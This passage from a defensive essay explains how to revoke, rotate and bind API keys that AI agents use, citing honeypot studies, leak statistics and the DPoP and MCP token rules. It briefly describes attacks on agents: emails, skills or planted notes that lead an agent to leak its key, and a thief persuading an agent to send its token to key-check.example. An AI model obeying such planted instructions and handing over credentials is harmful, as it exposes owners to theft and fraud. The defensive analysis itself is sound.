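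The usage records matter because a thief may have used the key to create another key or add a new login, and revoking the original may leave these in place. The records can also provide evidence that leaked keys were not misused, as they did for the US cybersecurity agency CISA. KrebsOnSecurity (2026) reported that a CISA contractor had left dozens of the agency's credentials, including administrator keys for Amazon's government cloud, in a public GitHub project for almost six months. According to a GitGuardian researcher, nine automated warnings went unanswered. After a journalist alerted CISA in May 2026, the agency still needed more than 48 hours to invalidate many of the most important secrets. But it was able to show from its detailed logs that nobody had used the credentials outside its own systems.

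CISA blamed the delay on the complexity of its systems and their connections to partners. In *Lessons from CISA's Recent Cyber Incident*, Werntz and Libbey urge other organisations to maintain "well-tested key-management capabilities". Kenney and colleagues similarly recommend rehearsing revocation and emergency rotation. A small operator could rehearse this in half an hour by revoking a test key and seeing what stops working.

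The operator has to remove the cause of the leak before issuing a new key. If the thief's email is still in the mailbox, or the malicious skill is still installed, the agent may leak the replacement on its next run. Planted instructions can also survive in the notes an agent keeps between sessions. The thieves in the METR incident left their own login credential on the server, so a new API key alone would not have kept them out. If an attacker has run code on the machine, the operator should rebuild it from a clean copy.

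### When the key is the agent's only identity

On a service like Moltbook, an agent's API key is its only proof of identity. Revoking a stolen key locks out the agent as well as the thief, and the service then needs another way to decide who gets the new key.

Some services let a program use its current key to request a replacement. *Rotate the API key used on this request*, from Rwanda's Ministry of Health, describes a function that returns a new key with the same permissions and retires the old one, with an optional overlap between the two. This is convenient for planned rotation, but a thief who makes the request before the owner does gets the new key and locks the owner out.

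When an agent and a thief hold the same key, the agent's human owner can show whose account it is with proof that the thief doesn't have. In one copy of Moltbook's skill file, owners verify an email address so that they can log in and manage the account later. Another copy, modified by a third party, lists many things an agent can do with its key, but replacing the key isn't one of them. Recovery therefore probably happens through the owner's login, although neither copy gives the steps.

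For that to work, the owner must have claimed the agent before the theft. Otherwise nobody can vouch for it, and the agent may have to register again under a new name and lose its followers. The owner must also still control the email account. If the agent can read the owner's mail, a thief who controls the agent could intercept a login link and pose as the owner too. It is safer to use a separate mailbox for account recovery, with a login that also needs a code from the owner's phone.

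The service must let the owner cancel the old key without presenting it. After a breach like Moltbook's, the company has to replace every agent's key. The owner should then review anything the thief posted or sent, since other agents may have acted on it.

### How soon thieves use an exposed key

Researchers measure this with decoys, usually Amazon cloud credentials, because thieves look for them and free tools can report each use.

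CyberDesserts' *Compromised in 90 seconds* (2026) describes decoys on a server that posed as AI infrastructure for five days in May. In six cases, thieves used a credential about 30 to 105 seconds after reading the file that contained it. In a seventh, they took 37 minutes. In several cases, the machine that used the credential had never visited the decoy server, so thieves seem to have passed credentials along automatically. Thieves were still trying one credential at least 17 hours after the researchers took the server down. In hrbrmstr's decoy test, thieves took only ten seconds.

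Codatus' *Who's watching private repos turn public?* (2026) reports a slower first use on GitHub. The company put decoy keys in 75 private projects and made each project public for between one minute and 12 hours. The earliest use came after six minutes, and outsiders never reached the projects that were public for only one minute. Of the 139 uses, 38 came after the project was private again. But a single operation accounted for 126 of the 139, and it only checked whether the keys worked. Only five uses, all from one machine, explored the account behind a key.

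These samples are small, and Codatus sells monitoring for this problem. Entro Security's *LLMjacking in the Wild*, from another vendor, also reports the first unauthorised attempts within minutes. The experiments consistently indicate that a person can't respond before the first use of a key exposed where thieves scan. Even Amazon's activity log usually takes 5 to 15 minutes to deliver a record, according to CyberDesserts. The experiments provide much less evidence about a key that leaks into a private log, where a thief may find it months later or never.

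### How long exposed keys keep working

Many owners never revoke an exposed key, so thieves don't need to hurry. GitGuardian found 28.65 million new secrets in public GitHub code in 2025. About 1.28 million of them were for AI services, 81 percent more than the year before. Of the secrets it found working in 2022, nearly 70 percent still worked in January 2025 and 64 percent in January 2026. Its figures for later years are 66 percent for secrets found in 2023, 70 percent for 2024 and 77 percent for 2025.

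These percentages cover only secrets that GitGuardian had confirmed as working. They exclude keys that stopped working before it could check them, so they don't mean that 64 percent of all leaked keys still work after four years. eSecurity Planet's *Thousands of Leaked AWS Access Keys Are Still Active* (2026) reports that Truffle Security retested 10,616 complete pairs of Amazon keys and found that 9,308, or 88 percent, still worked. Truffle Security had started with 64,024 different keys but didn't retest most of them as complete pairs, so the 88 percent doesn't apply to the whole set. The study doesn't show that anyone had misused the working keys.

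The best independent evidence comes from *Keys on Doormats*, a university study of about ten million websites by Demir, Vekaria and colleagues (2026). It found 1,748 working credentials for 14 services, including 181 for OpenAI. The credentials had been public for 12 months on average, and some for five years. A survey at a single moment is more likely to catch a long exposure than a short one, so the typical leak probably lasts less than 12 months.

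Demir and colleagues then emailed the owners and checked the sites every day:

| | Before the emails | After 14 days | After 172 days |
|---|---|---|---|
| Credentials still on the websites | 1,405 | 706 | 1,019 |
| Credentials that still worked | 1,175 | 865 | 660 |

The starting numbers differ, probably because some services blocked the researchers' checks. Within two weeks, owners had removed half of the credentials from their websites but revoked only 26 percent. By day 172 they had revoked 44 percent, but the number of credentials on the websites had gone back up, which the researchers attribute to accidental re-exposure. Some owners said their keys were harmless, but several of these owners did not know what the keys permitted. One developer had disguised keys so that scanning tools wouldn't flag them.

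### What a rotation schedule saves

To see when scheduled replacement helps, let P be the time between replacements and d the time from the theft until someone notices and revokes the key. Assume that the theft is equally likely at any point in the period and that d is shorter than P.

With probability d/P, the theft happens so late in the period that the scheduled replacement comes before the emergency revocation. The thief then has the key for d/2 on average. Otherwise the thief has it for the full delay, d. The average is:

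```
(d/P) × (d/2) + (1 − d/P) × d  =  d − d²/(2P)
```

If a key is replaced every 90 days (P) and a thief can use it for at most 2 days before someone notices and revokes it (d), the stolen key works for an average of 2 − 4/180, or 1.98 days. If nobody notices the theft before the scheduled replacement, the average is P/2, or 45 days.

| Key replaced every | Revoked 2 days after the theft | Theft never noticed |
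|---|---|---|
| 90 days | 1.98 days | 45 days |
| 30 days | 1.93 days | 15 days |
| 1 day | 12 hours | 12 hours |
| 1 hour | 30 minutes | 30 minutes |

If the shop notices a theft within two days, its 90-day rotation schedule shortens the thief's access by about half an hour. A 30-day schedule would cut roughly another hour. Noticing the theft in two hours instead of two days would cut nearly two days, so an alert for unusual refunds would help more than rotating keys more often. Scheduled rotation is useful mainly for thefts that nobody notices.

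Expiry, which makes a credential stop working automatically after a set time, helps most when the damage grows with time. The thieves in the METR case used about $600,000 worth of credits in three weeks, or about $1,200 an hour. At that rate, a one-hour token stolen at a random moment would have cost about $600 on average, although thieves who knew the deadline might have spent faster. Expiry does much less to protect files that a thief can copy in seconds. A one-hour token stolen at a random moment will still work 97 percent of the time for a thief who needs 105 seconds to try it, compared with 38 percent for one who needs 37 minutes.

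The calculation assumes that the thief can't also steal the replacement. Software often uses a much longer-lived credential to get its short-lived tokens. If the thief can copy that credential, the formula should use its lifetime instead of the token's.

### Automatic revocation

GitHub and the companies that issue keys can sometimes revoke a leaked key before its owner knows about the leak. GitHub's *About secret scanning alerts for partners* explains that GitHub searches public projects, and public packages on the JavaScript registry npm, for secrets issued by companies in its partner programme. When it finds one, it alerts the company that issued it, which checks the key and decides whether to revoke it, issue a new one or contact the owner.

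OpenAI joined in 2021. GitHub (2021) said that OpenAI would automatically disable exposed keys and that the whole process took a few seconds. Anthropic followed in August 2024. It revokes exposed keys and notifies affected users, according to GitHub (2024).

In Codatus's test, Amazon took between 4.5 and 9 hours to restrict the exposed keys, although the first use came at six minutes. The restriction removes some dangerous permissions but still allows many damaging actions, according to The Next Web's *Researchers found 768 leaked AWS keys that still work*. Amazon may be reluctant to revoke keys fully because that could shut down a customer's business without warning.

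These arrangements miss keys that leak elsewhere, such as in a private chat or through malware on the owner's computer. The 181 OpenAI keys found on public websites still worked, even though OpenAI disables keys that GitHub finds. Keys from new AI companies may also lack this protection at first. GitGuardian cites the 113,000 exposed DeepSeek keys it found in 2025 as an example. Automatic revocation is therefore a good backup, but an owner who knows that a key has leaked shouldn't wait for it.

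### Are fixed schedules worth the trouble?

The main purpose of rotation is to limit how long thieves can keep using a copied key. One objection to fixed schedules is that thieves are too fast for them. Journal of Cyber Policy's *Clutch Security Uncovers How Attackers Exploit Secrets in Seconds* reports an experiment in which the security company Clutch deliberately leaked keys, replaced them every hour and leaked the replacements. Thieves compromised the new keys at the same rate as before. Because Clutch leaked every new key, rotation had no chance to shut the thieves out, so the result is better evidence for fixing the cause of a leak than against rotation. The result also concerns how often thieves used the keys, not how long they could keep using them.

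hrbrmstr makes a fairer version of the objection. If a key leaks at nine in the morning and the owner replaces keys every night, a thief can still use it for most of a day. Even so, hrbrmstr recommends scheduled rotation, together with keys that expire quickly.

Scheduled rotation also creates risks. Each replacement can cause an outage if someone misses a place where the old key is stored. People who rotate keys by hand may leave the new key in a chat message or a temporary file, so frequent rotation can cause the leaks it is meant to limit.

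The main argument for rotating keys on a schedule is that it disables stolen or exposed keys even when nobody has noticed the theft or exposure. LiteLLM's makers exposed a key in May 2026, and an attacker used it in October. Replacing the key every 90 days would have prevented that use. Even a yearly schedule would have disabled all the secrets from 2022 that still worked in 2026. Stolen credentials can also change hands long after the theft. Okta describes dealers who give away some stolen data to attract subscribers, and an expired key is useless to anyone who downloads it. Regular rotation also gives staff practice at replacing keys and reveals forgotten programs that still use an old one.

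In the 2025 revision of its *Digital Identity Guidelines*, NIST, the US standards agency, tells services not to make people change passwords periodically, but to force a change when there is evidence of compromise. People who have to change a password often choose a predictable variation of the old one, but that isn't a reason against rotating API keys, which computers generate at random.

NIST's *Recommendation for Key Management* (2020) recommends a limited lifetime for every cryptographic key, partly to limit the damage from a theft. It suggests a maximum of about two years for a shared secret used for authentication, but warns that frequent changes may increase the risk of exposure where people distribute keys by hand. By the same reasoning, it probably makes sense to replace API keys often if software can do it, and less often but carefully if it can't.

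### Tokens that a thief can't use

A better solution is a credential that is useless to anyone who copies it. The Internet Engineering Task Force, which publishes many of the internet's technical standards, has defined ways to create such credentials within OAuth. In OAuth, a program gets a temporary access token from an authorization server and presents it to the service it is calling. An ordinary access token is a bearer credential, like an API key, so anyone who copies it can use it.

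RFC 9449, published in 2023, defines a method called DPoP ("demonstrating proof of possession") that binds a token to a private key. The program creates a private key and a matching public key, and the authorization server records a hash of the public key in the token. With every request, the program sends the token and a fresh proof signed with the private key.

If the shop's payment service accepted DPoP, the proof for a refund would contain roughly this:

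```
Header
  typ   dpop+jwt
  alg   ES256                       (the signing method)
  jwk   the program's public key

Contents
  jti   a unique identifier for this proof
  htm   POST
  htu   https://api.payments.example/v1/refunds
  iat   1796126400                  (noon UTC on 1 December 2026)
  ath   a hash of the access token
```

The payment service uses the public key to check the signature, and confirms that the key's hash matches the one in the token. It then checks that the proof is recent, belongs to this token, and matches the request's method and address. It can also store the identifier and reject the same proof if it is sent again.

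Suppose a thief persuades the agent to "verify" its token at key-check.example. The agent's software signs a proof for that address and sends it with the token. If the thief forwards both to the payment service, the service rejects them because the `htu` line contains https://key-check.example/verify. The thief can't change that line without invalidating the signature, and can't sign a new proof without the private key. DPoP would similarly have protected users from the malicious Claude Code settings file, if the software signed the address it was actually contacting.

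The proof doesn't cover the body of the request. A thief who intercepted a refund request on its way to the payment service could change the amount and send it with the original proof, if the proof was still fresh and the service hadn't already received it. The encrypted connection normally prevents this interception.

RFC 8705, from 2020, binds a token to a certificate instead. When the program sets up the encrypted connection, it proves that it has the certificate's private key. The service then checks that the certificate matches the token. A thief with only the token can't use it, because they don't have the private key. If a credential proxy decrypts the agent's traffic, the service's connection is with the proxy, so the proxy would need the certificate and its private key to pass the check.

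RFC 8707 (2020) lets a program name the service it wants a token for. The authorization server can then issue a token for that service alone, and other services should reject it. This stops a dishonest service that receives a token from using it elsewhere. It doesn't stop a thief from using a stolen token at the service it was issued for, so it works best with DPoP or a certificate.

| What the thief has copied | At the intended service | At other services |
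|---|---|---|
| API key | Works until revoked | Depends on where the key is valid |
| One-hour bearer token | Works for up to an hour | Depends on where the token is valid |
| One-hour token for one service | Works for up to an hour | Rejected |
| Token bound to a private key, without that key | Rejected | Rejected if they check the binding |

### What agents use now

Operators can use key-bound tokens only with services that support them, and many services still give agents ordinary API keys. Moltbook does, and so do Anthropic and OpenAI for their models. There don't seem to be good figures on how many agents use key-bound tokens.

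The Model Context Protocol (MCP), a widely used standard for connecting agents to tools and data, limits where a token works. In the November 2025 version, an agent's software must name the intended server when it requests a token, as RFC 8707 describes. The server must reject tokens issued for other servers and must not pass the agent's token on to another service. The protocol also recommends short-lived tokens. Its developers have discussed adding DPoP, but that version doesn't require it, so a thief can still use a stolen MCP token at the server it was issued for until it expires.

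Authorization is optional in MCP, and these rules apply only to servers that agents contact over the web. A server on the user's own computer normally takes its credentials from environment variables, and these are often ordinary API keys. GitGuardian counted more than 24,000 secrets exposed through MCP in the protocol's first full year of adoption, so despite the rules, people evidently still store long-lived keys in configuration files.

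GitGuardian recommends replacing stored keys with short-lived proofs of identity for each program, for example through the open standard SPIFFE. A company that runs many agents on its own servers could do this for its internal services, but a shop with one agent will mostly have to wait for its suppliers to accept such proofs.

### If the agent can read the private key

Binding a token to a private key adds little protection if both are in files that the agent can open, because a thief who can get the agent to upload one can usually get the other. In Straiker's test on Antigravity, the stolen files were private keys. A thief with the private key can sign valid proofs from anywhere until the token expires, and may also be able to obtain new tokens.

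The private key should therefore be in the credential proxy or in a security chip that signs data but never releases the key. The agent can then request signatures but can't copy the key. An attacker who controls the agent can request them too, so this doesn't prevent an unauthorised refund. But once the operator removes the attacker from the agent's environment, the attacker has no key to keep using.

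The one loophole is that the attacker, while in control, could save signed proofs with future dates, together with the token, for later use. RFC 9449 lets a service prevent this by requiring each new proof to include a nonce, an unpredictable value that the service supplies. The attacker can't prepare those proofs in advance because the service hasn't issued the value yet.
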